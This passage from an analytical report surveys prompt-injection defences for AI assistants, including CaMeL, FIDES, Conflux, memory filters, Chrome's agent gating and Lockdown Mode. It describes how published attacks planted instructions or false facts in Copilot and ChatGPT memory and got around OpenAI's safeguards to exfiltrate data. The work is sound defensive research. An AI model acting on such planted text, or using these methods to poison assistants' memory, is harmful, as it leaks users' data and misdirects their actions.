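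Attackers succeeded 152 times against the undefended assistant. AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted three successes against FIDES with its policies, but the researchers reviewed them by hand and rejected all three, leaving none. Across the tests, some of the cases they rejected were blocked calls that AgentDojo had scored as successes. Others were false text or Slack messages that the policies allowed but a user might object to.

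The labels also fitted the test unusually well. AgentDojo doesn't label its data, so the researchers marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. Someone labelling a real mailbox would not know in advance where the attacks will be.

For CaMeL, a recent comparison comes from a rival system. Hu, Jacob and colleagues (2026), in *Twin Agent*, ran it on AgentDojo with Gemini 2.5 Flash, a 2025 model:

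| Assistant | Tasks completed | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Undefended | 61.9% | 41.5% |
| CaMeL | 30.9% | 0.0% |
| Twin Agent | 62.9% | 0.1% |

Hu and colleagues gave CaMeL's planner three attempts to write a working program, instead of the original ten, to save computing time. They give the original paper's figure as about 35%, so the lower limit explains only a small part of the gap.

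Part of the difficulty is that the planner has to write code for results it hasn't seen. An ordinary assistant can work out the format from what the calendar returns, but CaMeL's planner needs the format in the tool's description. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add it to every tool's description before CaMeL did reasonably well. CaMeL's programs are also longer than ordinary tool calls, and *ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL significantly slower than defences that rely on prompts or filters.

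CaMeL reduces task completion less for stronger models. Peters-Gill and colleagues, including Shumailov from the original CaMeL team, tested five models on AssetOpsBench, a set of professional tasks that a directing assistant divides among four others. CaMeL reduced the share of completed tasks by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5.

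The researchers also divided AgentDojo's tools among several assistants and attacked them. On average, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL and 0.2% with it, and multi-CaMeL stopped the rest. The effect varied by model: Gemini 2.5 Pro went from 24.6% to 0.4%, while GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL. On this benchmark, CaMeL reduced the number of tasks GPT-5.5 completed without measurably improving its security, although the researchers warn that stronger attacks might succeed. They ran CaMeL without any data policies, so their figures measure the protection of the plan, not the reader tags that a case like Ana's agenda depends on.

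### Twin Agent and Conflux: looser rules

Twin Agent doesn't fix the plan in advance. Hu and colleagues pair an Explore Agent, which reads everything but can't act, with a Safe Agent, which acts but can't read outside material. At each step, the Explore Agent may send the Safe Agent a hint about what to do next, limited to 200 characters on AgentDojo and 100 on the other tests. A detector screens the hints for injections. Hu and colleagues assume that a strong model is hard to hijack with so little text.

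The hints make a large difference when the task itself is in outside text. On coding tasks that began with a stranger's bug report, GPT-5.2 fixed 62.5% of the bugs with hints of up to 100 characters and none without hints. Longer hints helped more but gave attackers more opportunity. With the 100-character limit, running two agents cost about twice as much as running one.

Hu and colleagues then attacked the coding version with knowledge of its design. In separate tests, the Explore Agent copied the attacker's text into its hint every time. The complete system carried out the attacker's goal in 11 of 232 tasks (4.7%). When the researchers ran those 11 tasks five more times each, no attack succeeded, so the earlier successes seem to be partly chance, and an attacker could keep trying. Hu and colleagues offer no formal guarantee. Twin Agent limits how much an outsider can tell the acting model,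 though 200 characters is enough for a false account number. It has no reader tags, so it does not limit where private data may go.

*Conflux* (Buckley and Schroeder de Witt, 2026) lets outside text influence the assistant freely but restricts what the assistant can do afterwards. It records everyone whose information influenced an action and allows the action only if each of them has permission to take it. Suppose Ava asks an assistant to update a customer's record with the status from Ben's report. Conflux allows the update if both Ava and Ben may edit the record. It looks up permissions in the organisation's existing access system, so nobody has to write a separate policy for each task.

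This is close to the rule from Willison's exchange with Bista, that a model reading someone's text should have only that person's privileges. In the Gemini case, the outsider who wrote the invitation presumably had no right to create events as the user, so Conflux would have blocked the new event. It might also block many of the user's own bookings, because the assistant has to read the calendar to find a free hour, and every invitation in it affects which hours are free. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt suggest planning the work so that the assistant acts before it reads a restricted person's text, but the assistant can't book a free hour until it has read the calendar.

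The Conflux paper proves that Conflux never allows an action if anyone recorded as having influenced the model lacks permission for it. The proof assumes, among other things, that the system has correctly recorded the author of every input that influenced the model. The paper makes no claim about how many tasks an assistant could complete. Its AgentDojo runs only read data, so they don't test whether Conflux blocks harmful actions.

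### Reading widely and sending little

CaMeL and FIDES can handle the tenant's open-ended question, "What have I forgotten this month?", without limiting what the assistant reads, because only the tenant will see the answer.

The difficulty comes when the tenant wants to use the answer. In FIDES, an email's permitted readers are its sender and recipients. The landlord's message has the readers {tenant, landlord}, and the electricity company's has {tenant, company}. Anything that combines the two has only one permitted reader, the tenant. Two correspondents are enough to produce the most restrictive label possible, and a month's mail has dozens. The list of forgotten things is also untrusted, because any of those people could have influenced it.

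Suppose the list includes a reminder to send the landlord a meter reading, which appears in the electricity company's letter. The tenant tells the assistant to send it. The number carries the labels of the whole month's mail if the assistant takes it from the list, but only the letter's labels if the assistant goes back to the letter. So labels spread less when the assistant works with individual values than with summaries. But the landlord isn't a permitted reader in either case, so the assistant has to ask the tenant or treat the request as permission.

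Costa and colleagues allow for the second option, in which a policy can accept a disclosure when only trusted text led to it, assuming the user intended it. That seems reasonable for a number from one named letter. It is riskier for an item from the list, because an outsider may have chosen what the list contains, even though the tenant's request is trusted. The problem would grow with stored memories, which can combine years of sources.

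Hu and colleagues object that systems like CaMeL and FIDES often make an assistant much less useful and require rigid interfaces or task-specific policies. Even for a benchmark, the FIDES researchers wrote tool wrappers to label each field of every result, wrote policies, and hand-tuned the instructions that teach the planner to use variables. A company would have to do this for every tool it connects and keep the labels correct as the tools change.

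Costa and colleagues, who designed FIDES, answer that many labels already exist in some form. An email lists its sender and recipients, and mail servers can verify a sender's address. The FIDES team used three general policies for all of AgentDojo and reused the same planner instructions, with small changes, across settings and models. Peters-Gill and colleagues similarly call writing the extra tool descriptions a modest job that a developer does once. For labels that spread too far, Costa and colleagues point to research that works out which messages influenced a model's answer, so that the answer carries only those messages' labels.

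This reply works better for secrecy than for trust. A company usually knows who may open a document, and an email's address fields are a fair guide to its readers, though people also forward emails. But, as with ROPE, a verified address shows who sent a message, not where its contents came from. Costa and colleagues suggest that a system could mark a document as trusted after an injection detector has passed it, but they warn that this can weaken the guarantee because such detectors miss some attacks.

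Better models have already reduced the loss of usefulness and will probably reduce it further, but only where the planner writes poor programs or confuses its variables. Many of AgentDojo's banking tasks ask the assistant to read a file and do what it says. FIDES refuses to make a payment after reading an untrusted file, and would do so even with a stronger model. Costa and colleagues count this refusal as the system working correctly.

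## Copilot and ChatGPT memory: when stored history carries the attack

CaMeL and FIDES track data within a single session, but Copilot and ChatGPT also keep notes between sessions. An outsider who gets one sentence into those notes can influence conversations weeks later, when the sentence looks like any other note about the user.

### How assistants keep memory

The program around a language model saves text and adds some of it to later prompts, because the model itself retains nothing between conversations. OpenAI's help page *Memory in ChatGPT* describes several kinds of stored material, and Microsoft's assistants keep similar kinds.

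| Store | Example | Who writes to it | When the assistant reads it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Saved memories | "The rent is due on the 1st" | The user, by asking, or the model, when a detail seems useful | In later chats, including new ones |
| Summary of past chats | A profile of the user's work, home and preferences | A background process that goes through old chats | When it seems likely to improve an answer |
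| Old conversations | Last month's chat about the lease | Anyone whose text entered the chat | When something in them seems relevant to the new request |

None of these products gives outsiders permission to write saved memories, but what the model saves depends on everything in its context, so a stranger's web page can lead it to save a sentence just as the user's request can. *Trust No AI* (2024) reported this in ChatGPT in the year OpenAI introduced memory. Websites, documents and images could plant instructions that sent the user's later conversations to an attacker.

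ChatGPT's memory can now also draw on the user's stored files and on connected apps such as Gmail, depending on plan and region. An outsider's email could therefore influence an answer through memory even if nobody had saved anything from it.

Memory also benefits users. Windows Report's *OpenAI Upgrades ChatGPT Memory With Smarter Recall and Better Personalization* cites OpenAI's own figures that factual recall rose from 67.9% in 2025 to 82.8% in 2026, and adherence to users' preferences from 55.3% to 71.3%. These figures compare two versions of memory, so they don't show how much worse ChatGPT would do without it.

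### CoSnitch: a web page that wrote to Copilot's memory

Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes three flaws in the consumer version of Copilot. Two of them let an attacker steal data from a user's connected mail, files and calendar after one click on a link. Copilot sent the data out in the address of a web page it fetched.

The third flaw involved Copilot's memory and needed no connected account. When the user asked Copilot to summarise a web page that contained hidden instructions, Copilot returned a normal-looking summary but also saved the attacker's text as a memory. In one demonstration, the saved text was a claim that a known software vulnerability posed no risk, which could have led the user to leave it unpatched.

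The planted text did not expire. Changing the password, ending all sessions and re-enrolling the device made no difference, because the text was in the account's memory, not on the device. The user had to delete it in the memory settings. Microsoft says turning personalisation off also makes Copilot forget what it has learned from conversations, but then it stops personalising its answers altogether.

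Varonis reported the flaws in December 2025, and Microsoft released patches on 18 August 2026. TechRadar gives the identifier CVE-2026-24301 and says Microsoft fixed the flaws on its own servers. Varonis saw no evidence of real attacks. It doesn't say what the patch changed or whether Microsoft looked for entries that someone had already planted. A patch that only prevents new writes would leave those entries in place.

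Microsoft had repaired a similar flaw shortly before. *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, by Johann Rehberger of Embrace The Red, describes documents that could write to memory in both consumer and Microsoft 365 Copilot. Microsoft told him it had fixed this by 6 December 2025. He thinks the Microsoft 365 fix was more model training and more filtering of incoming content. If the consumer product got the same fix, attacks through web pages may still have been possible.

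Companies have already tried to influence assistants' memory for commercial gain. Microsoft (2026) found links on public websites that opened an assistant with a ready-made prompt telling it to remember the company behind the link as a good source. Microsoft counted more than 50 such prompts from 31 companies in 60 days, according to Aviatrix, a security vendor. The count covers attempts, not how many assistants saved the recommendation.

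### ZombieAgent: a rule that worked in one order

When the security company Radware tested ChatGPT in September 2025, OpenAI already had two rules against attacks through memory. ChatGPT could not use memory and a connector, such as the one for Gmail, in the same chat, and it would not open a web address that an attacker had placed in memory.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the researchers got past both defenses. The ban on combining connectors with memory worked in only one order, so ChatGPT could still read its memory first and then use a connector. A file that the user shared in the chat could also write to memory. The researchers used such a file to store an instruction to read an email from the attacker whenever the user wrote something. The email supplied the web addresses, so ChatGPT didn't have to take them from memory.

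The attack could reach connected accounts, past chats and stored memories, and it sent the data out in web requests from OpenAI's servers. Radware also altered a user's stored medical history, which led ChatGPT to give harmful advice even though no data left.

The user only had to share the file once, and starting a new chat didn't remove the instructions. Deleting the chat that contained the file might not have removed them either, because OpenAI stores saved memories separately from chats. The user had to find the memories and delete them.

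OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December, 81 days after the first report. Radware doesn't describe the fix. Particle.news' *Radware’s ‘ZombieAgent’ Bypasses ChatGPT Fixes, Forcing New OpenAI Restrictions*, a summary of press coverage, reports that ChatGPT now opens links from emails only if they are well-known public links. That closes off a way to send data out, but it would not prevent a file from planting a false medical history in ChatGPT's memory.

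### GhostWriter: how often planted memories work

CoSnitch and ZombieAgent show that such attacks are possible. *When Agents Remember Too Much* (Torres, Shrestha and Misra, 2026) measures how often they succeed. The paper's attack, GhostWriter, works against any user to whom the attacker can send an email or a calendar invitation. In one scenario, the attacker sends a message claiming that a colleague has a new email address. The assistant saves the address, and when the user later asks it to write to that colleague, the email goes to the attacker.

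The researchers, at New Mexico State University, tested five memory systems, each with four models: OpenAI's GPT-5.4-mini, Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash, Meta's Llama 3.1 8B and DeepSeek-V4-Flash. They followed the same procedure each time:

1. They gave the assistant 32 emails and calendar events from an invented working week and kept a copy of the memory it built.
2. They sent one malicious message and checked whether its content reached the memory.
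3. They made an ordinary request and checked whether the assistant retrieved the planted entry and acted on it.
4. They restored the clean memory before the next scenario. There were 16 scenarios, and they ran each one five times.

The assistants stored the planted content about 98% of the time, and it changed what they did an average of about 60% of the time. The lowest rate was 28%, for Llama with ExpeL, a system that stores examples of past tasks instead of facts. Ordinary AgentDojo injections reached memory about as often but took effect later in at most 16.7% of cases, because they weren't written to match a future request.

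GhostWriter's messages were also hard to detect. DataFilter, a model trained to find injections, caught none of them. When the researchers prompted GPT-5.4-mini to look for injections, it flagged 85% of the messages phrased as orders but only 6% of those phrased as false statements or polite requests.

The 98% figure reflects the fact that these systems turn nearly every incoming message into a memory. ChatGPT and Copilot save selectively, so their rate could be much lower. Torres and colleagues also used small, cheap models. *When Claws Remember but Do Not Tell* (2026) found large differences between models running the self-hosted assistant OpenClaw. One crude attack wrote to memory 96.4% of the time with Grok 4.1 Fast, while an automated search for attacks never fully succeeded against Claude Sonnet 4.6.

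### A false address in March, a theft in June

Suppose the tenant's assistant reads an email in March saying that the letting agent has a new address, and saves the address. It belongs to an outsider. In June the tenant asks the assistant to send their bank statements to the agent.

Limiting permissions in each session doesn't prevent this. In March the assistant needs permission only to read mail and save a memory. In June it needs to read files and send an email, as the tenant asked. Willison's three conditions for theft are all met, but across two sessions, because the untrusted text arrives in March and the private data leaves in June. A Progent policy would not help if the model that wrote the policy looked up the agent's address in memory. CaMeL's tags could stop the email only if the assistant saved them with the address and restored them in June.

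A log of the June session shows a normal request, a memory lookup and an email to the address on file. To discover the fraud, an investigator has to connect the June log to a message from March. According to Microsoft, Microsoft 365 Copilot does not record memory actions in the audit log. The tenant may also have deleted the March chat, while the saved address remained.

Anomaly detection has trouble catching either step of the attack, because saving a contact's new address and writing to a saved contact are both normal. A detector that learns from past sessions may do even worse. If the tenant has written to the agent every week since March, the false address is familiar by June, and an email to the agent's real address would stand out. This follows from how such detectors work, but neither Torres and colleagues nor the other memory studies here tested it.

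### Keeping outsiders' text out of memory

One remedy is to forbid memory writes in any session that has read outside content. That would have stopped the attacks through the web page in CoSnitch, the file in ZombieAgent and the emails in GhostWriter. The rule would also have to cover the background process that summarises old chats, or the same text could enter memory a day later.

None of these studies measured the strict rule, but its main drawback is clearly that it would block useful memories. The tenant could not ask the assistant to remember the landlord's phone number from an email. An office assistant reads other people's text in most sessions, so it would learn little about the user's work.

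Rehberger proposes a milder version, in which the assistant saves a memory automatically only when the user's own message clearly asks for it, and otherwise suggests the memory and waits for approval. This would have exposed ZombieAgent's strange instructions, but it would do less against the letting agent's new address, which the tenant would probably approve.

Torres and colleagues let a model judge each entry. The strictest version of their defence, AM-Sentry, scores an entry from 0 to 1 on seven points. It rejects the entry at once if the score for harmlessness is below 0.6. Otherwise it computes

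F = 0.6 · C + 0.4 · N,

where C is the average of the scores for sensitivity and source, and N is the average for the other four: contradiction, instructions, verifiability and usefulness. It rejects the entry if F is below 0.4. A second model then looks for signs that the entry hijacked the first one.

The formula gives the source little weight. An entry from an untrusted stranger scores 0 for source, but if it scores 1 on everything else, F is 0.6 × 0.5 + 0.4 × 1 = 0.7, and the entry passes. Protection against a plausible stranger therefore depends mostly on the model's judgement of what the text could do.

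With three of the four models, this version reduced the share of planted entries that reached memory to 15% on average. With Llama, 77% still got through. A second filter, which checked memories when the assistant retrieved them, cut the attack success rate to below 12% for those three models and to 20% for Llama. The attackers didn't know about the defence, so these are best-case figures.

The loss of usefulness was mostly small. With A-Mem, one of the five memory systems, the score for how closely answers matched a reference fell by 0.01 to 0.04 for most models. Llama's score fell more because it rejected many legitimate memories. ExpeL also did worse as the rules became stricter.

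Bhowmik (2026), in *The Price of Safety*, ran similar filters on five long conversations with no attack in them. A filter at retrieval dropped 2.2% of the memories it checked, which removed at least one memory from 14.9% of questions. A blind audit of 50 dropped memories found a good reason to drop only two. The effect on accuracy was too small to detect (+0.6 percentage points, 95% interval −2.6 to +3.8), and the filter added 3.0% to the tokens processed. The assistant usually had other memories that answered the question, but losing a single memory about an allergy could matter far more than this average suggests.

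### Recording where each memory came from

An assistant could instead save the letting agent's address with a note that it came from an unknown sender. The note helps only if it affects what the assistant later does with the address.

Trust scores that a model derives from the text alone are unreliable. *Memory Poisoning Attack and Defense on Memory Based LLM-Agents* (2026) reports one experiment in which the scoring rejected every entry, including harmless ones, and another in which it gave 54 planted entries perfect scores. *When Does Belief-Based Agent Memory Help?* (2026) therefore caps the score by origin:

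trust = min(trust from origin, trust from content).

If an unknown sender has an origin score of 0.2, a convincing email that scores 0.9 for its content still gets 0.2. Like FIDES's labels, the cap also has to apply to anything the assistant derives from the text. For example, Microsoft says that its 365 Copilot merges related memories. A merged entry would need the lowest trust score of its parts, so one email could reduce trust in several facts the user had supplied.

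*Forget to Improve* (2026) tested a filter that checks where a stored entry came from and whether it reads like an instruction. Attacks using up to 15 planted entries never succeeded against the filter, but they succeeded about 80% of the time without the origin check. Attackers who could forge an entry's origin sometimes succeeded.

A false statement that contains no instruction is harder to detect. *Utility Under Attack* (Karunanidhi, 2026) tested Aegis, a memory system that Karunanidhi helps to build, on 120 questions about long chat histories. For each question, three false entries contradicted the true answer, for instance by changing the number of a user's playlists from 20 to 15. The false entries made up 1.2% of the memory and reduced accuracy from 85.0% to 30.0%. Aegis screens text before saving it. This screening had caught 83.2% of indirect injections in another test, but it refused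 none of the 360 false entries because it would have needed to know the answers already to recognise them.

Aegis also prefers entries from trusted channels when it retrieves memories. Leaving aside other parts of its formula, it ranks each entry by

score = w · similarity + v · trust,

where similarity measures how closely the entry matches the question. An outsider's entry wins if its advantage in similarity is greater than v/w times its disadvantage in trust. With the original weights, that threshold was 0.175. The false entries had gained 0.32 by resembling the question, so the preference made no detectable difference.

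Karunanidhi then raised the weight on trust until an outside entry lost 0.245 points. A perfect match adds at most 0.45, so the threshold rose to 0.245/0.45, or about 0.54. When most outside entries were harmless, the heavier weight raised accuracy under attack from 31.7% to 70.0%. But when the true answers also came from outside, Aegis retrieved none of them across the 120 questions, and accuracy fell to 4.2%.

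Much of what the tenant wants remembered, such as the agent's phone number, the new rent and the date of the boiler inspection, arrives in other people's emails. Karunanidhi suggests reserving a limited number of places among the retrieved memories for outside entries, but has not built this.

### Expiry and separate stores

If memories from outside expired after 30 days, the address saved in March would be gone by June. *Forget to Improve* offers some evidence for a related approach, removing entries that prove less useful. Within three rounds, planted entries fell to a fifth of their original level, while genuine ones stayed. A fixed expiry date would also delete genuine entries, so the tenant would have to repeat the boiler date. An attack that took effect within the 30 days would still work.

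Separate stores limit how far a planted entry can spread. With ChatGPT's project-only memory, chats can refer to other conversations in the same project but not to any outside it. If the tenant kept all correspondence about the flat in one project, a false entry from that correspondence could not influence a chat about their health elsewhere. It could still misdirect the bank statements. The tenant would also lose answers that need both sets of chats, such as whether a medical appointment clashes with the boiler inspection.

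ChatGPT's locked chats can use existing memories, but new messages in them don't personalise other chats while the lock is on. This suits a conversation about a stranger's document, provided the user remembers to lock the chat first.

### User review and the controls in current products

User review of stored memories works best for entries that look odd. A user who finds an instruction to open a stranger's email before every answer will probably delete it. A false address beside a plausible name is harder to spot, especially if the user never knew the real address.

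The table compares the controls in OpenAI's and Microsoft's memory documentation, as of October 2026 for ChatGPT and May 2026 for the main Microsoft 365 page. "None listed" means the documentation describes no such control.

| Remedy | ChatGPT | Microsoft 365 Copilot | Consumer Copilot |
|---|---|---|---|
| No memory writes after reading outside content | No automatic rule; users can choose a temporary chat, which saves no memories | None listed; administrators can't restrict what Copilot saves | None listed |
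| Origin of each memory | A list of sources under some answers | None listed | None listed |
| Expiry of saved memories | None listed | Kept until the user deletes them | None listed |
| Separate stores | Project-only memory | None listed | None listed |
| User review | Summary and saved memories that users can correct or delete | "Memory updated" notice and a list in settings | Summary on request; users can delete one item or everything |

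The tenant could use ChatGPT's list of sources to trace a wrong address back to the email it came from. OpenAI warns that the list may not include everything that shaped an answer, and that the memory summary also leaves things out. Consumer Copilot users can ask "What do you know about me?", but the same model writes the reply, so a planted instruction might influence that reply too.

Removing a memory can take several steps. OpenAI advises users to delete the saved memory, the chat where they first shared the information, and any copies in files or connected apps. Microsoft tells Microsoft 365 users to remove both the saved memory and whatever Copilot has inferred from past chats.

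A Microsoft 365 administrator can search for saved memories across the organisation and delete them. Turning the memory feature off is quicker, but it only stops Copilot from using saved memories. They remain in a hidden folder in each user's mailbox, and Copilot could use them again if the administrator turned the feature back on. A policy that deletes Copilot chats after three months also leaves the memories from those chats in place.

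## Chrome and ChatGPT: limits in shipped products and the user's approval

Few people will write a policy for their assistant or label their own mail, so most depend on the limits its maker builds in. Google's browsing agent in Chrome may use only websites relevant to the current task. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT, which users can turn on, removes features regardless of the task. Chrome also asks the user to approve some actions before they happen.

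### Chrome: a list of sites for each task

Chrome's agent uses Google's Gemini models to click, type and move between pages, often in a browser where the user has already logged in to their mail, bank and shops. Browsers normally stop one site from reading another's data, but a hijacked agent could carry it across. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, sets out Google's design. Suppose the tenant asks the agent to collect ingredients from a recipe page and put them in a supermarket's online basket:

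1. A model called the planner reads the request and the pages, and proposes the sites it needs.
2. A gating function that sees no page content decides which of these sites are relevant. It puts the recipe site on a list for reading only, and the supermarket on a list where the agent may also click and type.
3. Chrome withholds content from other sites. If the recipe page contains an advert from elsewhere, the model never receives it.
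4. The planner proposes an action, such as adding flour to the basket. A second Gemini model, the User Alignment Critic, sees a description of the action but not the pages, and approves it only if it serves the request.
5. After a rejection the planner tries something else. If it keeps failing, it can hand control back to the tenant.

The agent needs a similar check before it moves to a new site. A fixed rule also requires any web address the model writes itself to be a known public address, which closes one route for data to leave.

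If the planner followed an instruction in a comment under the recipe and tried to open the tenant's webmail, the gating function should block it, because mail has nothing to do with groceries. The lists help much less when the task is about mail, because the landlord's messages, the bank's letters and the send button are all on one website. Parker also writes that the first version had only the list of sites where the agent could act, and not yet the separate list of sites it could read.

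Parker names CaMeL as a partial inspiration for the critic, but the critic, unlike CaMeL's interpreter, is a model making a judgement. Parker claims only that web content cannot poison it directly. An outsider might still influence it through the planner, which has read the page and proposes the action, just as injected text reached Twin Agent's hints. The critic is not given the pages, so it cannot check whether an account number came from the landlord or from a stranger.

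Some actions also need the user's confirmation. Chrome asks before the agent opens any site on a fixed list of sensitive sites, such as those of banks and medical services. It also asks before the agent signs in with a saved password, which the model cannot read directly. Before a purchase, a payment, a message or another consequential action, the agent "will try to" pause for permission or let the user complete the step. This promise is weaker because the system must first recognise the action as consequential.

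Google attacks the agent with automated tests and offers outside researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating a serious breach. Parker does not report how often the attacks succeed.

### Lockdown Mode: fewer exits for people at higher risk

OpenAI launched Lockdown Mode in February 2026 for organisations, including companies, universities and healthcare providers. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) says the mode is meant for a small group of users, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and that most people don't need it. In June, OpenAI began offering it on personal accounts too.

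The mode is meant to stop the last step of a theft, when data leaves. For example, ChatGPT can browse only pages that OpenAI has already stored, so no request goes out to an attacker's server. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the help page for the setting, lists the changes:

| Feature | In Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Stored pages only, which may be out of date |
| Images | Answers may not display them, and ChatGPT may not fetch them from the web; uploads and image generation still work |
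| Deep research and agent mode, which work through many web pages unattended | Off |
| Network access for code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editor | Off |
| Downloading files for data analysis | Off; files that the user uploads still work |
| Apps on personal and small-business accounts | No live access to outside services and no changes to them, where these conflict with the mode's protections |
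| Apps in workspaces that an administrator manages | Whatever the administrator allows |
| Memory, file uploads and sharing of conversations | Unchanged |
| Network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding assistant | Unchanged |

Blocking images from the web closes the type of channel that three of the five Copilot chains used to send data out. Limiting browsing to stored pages should also stop web requests like those in ZombieAgent. But the mode does not restrict memory, so a shared file could still plant a false medical history there. OpenAI acknowledges that injections can still reach ChatGPT through stored pages and uploaded files and make its answers wrong.

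The main way data can still leave is through apps in managed workspaces. OpenAI advises administrators not to allow any action whose result an outsider might see. In the Gemini case, creating a calendar event was such an action. Codex can also reach the network, and OpenAI warns that unforeseen combinations of features may leak data.

On a personal account, the mode could take away most of what the tenant wanted. Without live access to their mailbox, ChatGPT can't search for the landlord's messages, so the tenant would have to upload them by hand. They can turn the mode off for a single chat, but they are most likely to do so when they need live mail or web pages, which is when an outsider's text can do the most harm.

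Willison welcomed the mode because its limits are fixed and no AI system evaluates them. He also inferred that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect data against a determined attacker. Chrome's approach restricts everyday use less, since the agent can still visit any site that a task requires, but it depends on a component correctly judging what each task requires.

### How often people approve

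Other assistants rely on approval even more than Chrome does. For *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) tried five products from OpenAI and Anthropic in May and June 2026. In ChatGPT's ordinary chat, they had to approve every action covered by a permission setting and found no way to do so in advance. That is stricter than the connectors Zhu and colleagues examined in late 2025, which acted without further confirmation. ChatGPT's agent mode, which operates a remote browser, offered no permission settings for that browser.

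Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant, used to ask for approval before most commands and file changes. Users accepted 93% of these prompts, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. Another Anthropic post, *How we contain Claude across products*, gives the same figure and attributes it to usage data. By August 2026 the rate was 97%, according to the company's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). None of the three posts gives the number of users or the period its figure covers.

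Because most commands are harmless, even a careful reviewer would approve nearly all of them, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless. The same users rejected 39% of the plans Claude Code showed them, which suggests that they do object when they read something closely.

Anthropic also ran an experiment in which a research vendor hired 1,053 testers for a coding study without telling them what it was measuring. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command, and 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic published this while making an automatic reviewer the default, so the result supports its product decision. People may also take more care on their own computers than the testers did, since none of the testers' own files were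 at risk, but that doesn't easily explain why refusals fell as sessions went on.

Independent evidence suggests that people approve too much even when they see few prompts. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, asked 113 people from outside the software industry to supervise a simulated assistant handling mail, travel and shopping. It attempted 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had requested. Yan compared three ways of deciding:

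| How the assistant got permission | Prompts per person | Unrequested actions that went ahead |
|---|---|---|
| The user approved every action | 18 | 40% |
| A model allowed some actions and asked about the rest | 10 | 46% |
| The user set rules in advance for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data | 10.9 | 60% |

Fewer prompts did not lead to better decisions here, though 18 prompts are too few to tire anyone much. The rules did worst mainly because people avoided deciding in advance. They chose "ask me" for 81% of the rules, then approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions they were asked about.

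Yan's test involved no attacker, and some of the extra actions looked helpful. When the assistant needed approval for every action, 88% of people allowed an unrequested call to the airport to confirm a flight, but only 35% let it read private messages. People would therefore be more likely to approve an injected action that resembles the airport call than one that reads private messages.

Some users stop reviewing altogether. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of trouble with AI agents and users' files. In 80 of them, users had let the agent act without asking, and in 31, prompts didn't make the effect of a command clear. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), an interview and survey study, software practitioners watched an agent more or less closely depending on its apparent risk, their trust in it, and their own time and fatigue.

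### A request to send bank statements

Consider the false address that reached the tenant's assistant in March. In June the tenant asks it to send their bank statements to the letting agent, and the assistant shows this request:

```
Send this email?

To:          Letting agent <lettings@example.com>
Subject:     Bank statements for tenancy renewal
Attachment:  statements-march-to-may.pdf

[Allow]   [Deny]
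```

The tenant asked the assistant to email these statements to the agent, and the approval request matches that except for the address, which is wrong. The tenant relies on the assistant to remember the agent's address. They could catch the fraud by comparing the address in the request with the one on an old letter, but nothing in the request gives them a reason to.

The approval prompt would work better in the original hijack, because the tenant wanted only a summary of the landlord's messages and a request to email bank documents to a stranger would look out of place. Even then, instead of suspecting an outsider, the tenant might take the request for a mistake or for the sort of unrequested help that many of Yan's participants approved.

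A better prompt would explain where the address came from. It could add that the assistant saved this address from an unknown sender's email in March, and that the tenant's earlier messages to the agent went elsewhere. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested how much such information helps. Their 80 volunteers each judged 12 requests from an assistant, half of them unsafe. In one example, a user wants an auditor to receive only totals, and planted instructions make the assistant put the raw invoices into the file it sends. Each volunteer saw one of four kinds of prompt:

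| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact details of the action as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| The user's original instruction and a full log as well | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| The same facts, arranged to show the action's overall effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

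People clearly made better decisions when they had more information, but the difference between the last two rows could be due to chance. Even with the best prompt, people approved almost a quarter of the unsafe requests. Half the requests they saw were unsafe, which should have kept them alert, whereas the tenant might see hundreds of genuine requests before the false one.

The fuller confirmation prompts also depend on the assistant keeping a trustworthy record of where its data came from, much like CaMeL's tags. Software with such a record can block some actions without asking the user, so it may need to show far fewer prompts. Hossain and colleagues tested this kind of block with a small open model, Llama 3.1 8B. The block reduced the number of attacked runs in which unsafe actions went ahead from 52 to 6 out of 120, while the number of harmless tasks completed fell from 104 to 100 out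 of 120.

### Sandboxes and automatic reviewers in place of prompts

Anthropic first addressed approval fatigue with a sandbox. Its *Beyond permission prompts* (20 October 2025) describes two limits that the operating system enforces on the commands Claude Code runs. The commands can change files only in the current project's folder, and they can reach the internet only through a separate program that checks each destination against an approved list. Claude Code runs commands within those limits without asking, and prompts the user when a command needs something outside them.

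An assistant needs limits on both network and file access. If hijacked, it could use open network access to send out any secret it could read, or use unrestricted file access to tamper with the system and escape the network limit.

In Anthropic's internal use, sandboxing reduced permission prompts by 84%. The company doesn't give a sample size, time period or method for that figure. The figure measures how often users were interrupted, not how many attacks were prevented. If the same reduction held elsewhere, a developer who saw 100 prompts a day would see 16, and might read those more carefully.

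A sandbox suits a coding assistant better than an email assistant. Much of a programmer's work can stay inside one folder, but the tenant's assistant has to send messages to other people. It would need a list of permitted recipients, which is closer to a Progent policy than to an isolated machine. Files can still leak through an approved destination. In an attack on Claude Cowork, Anthropic's assistant for office work, files left through Anthropic's own service, which the sandbox had to allow.

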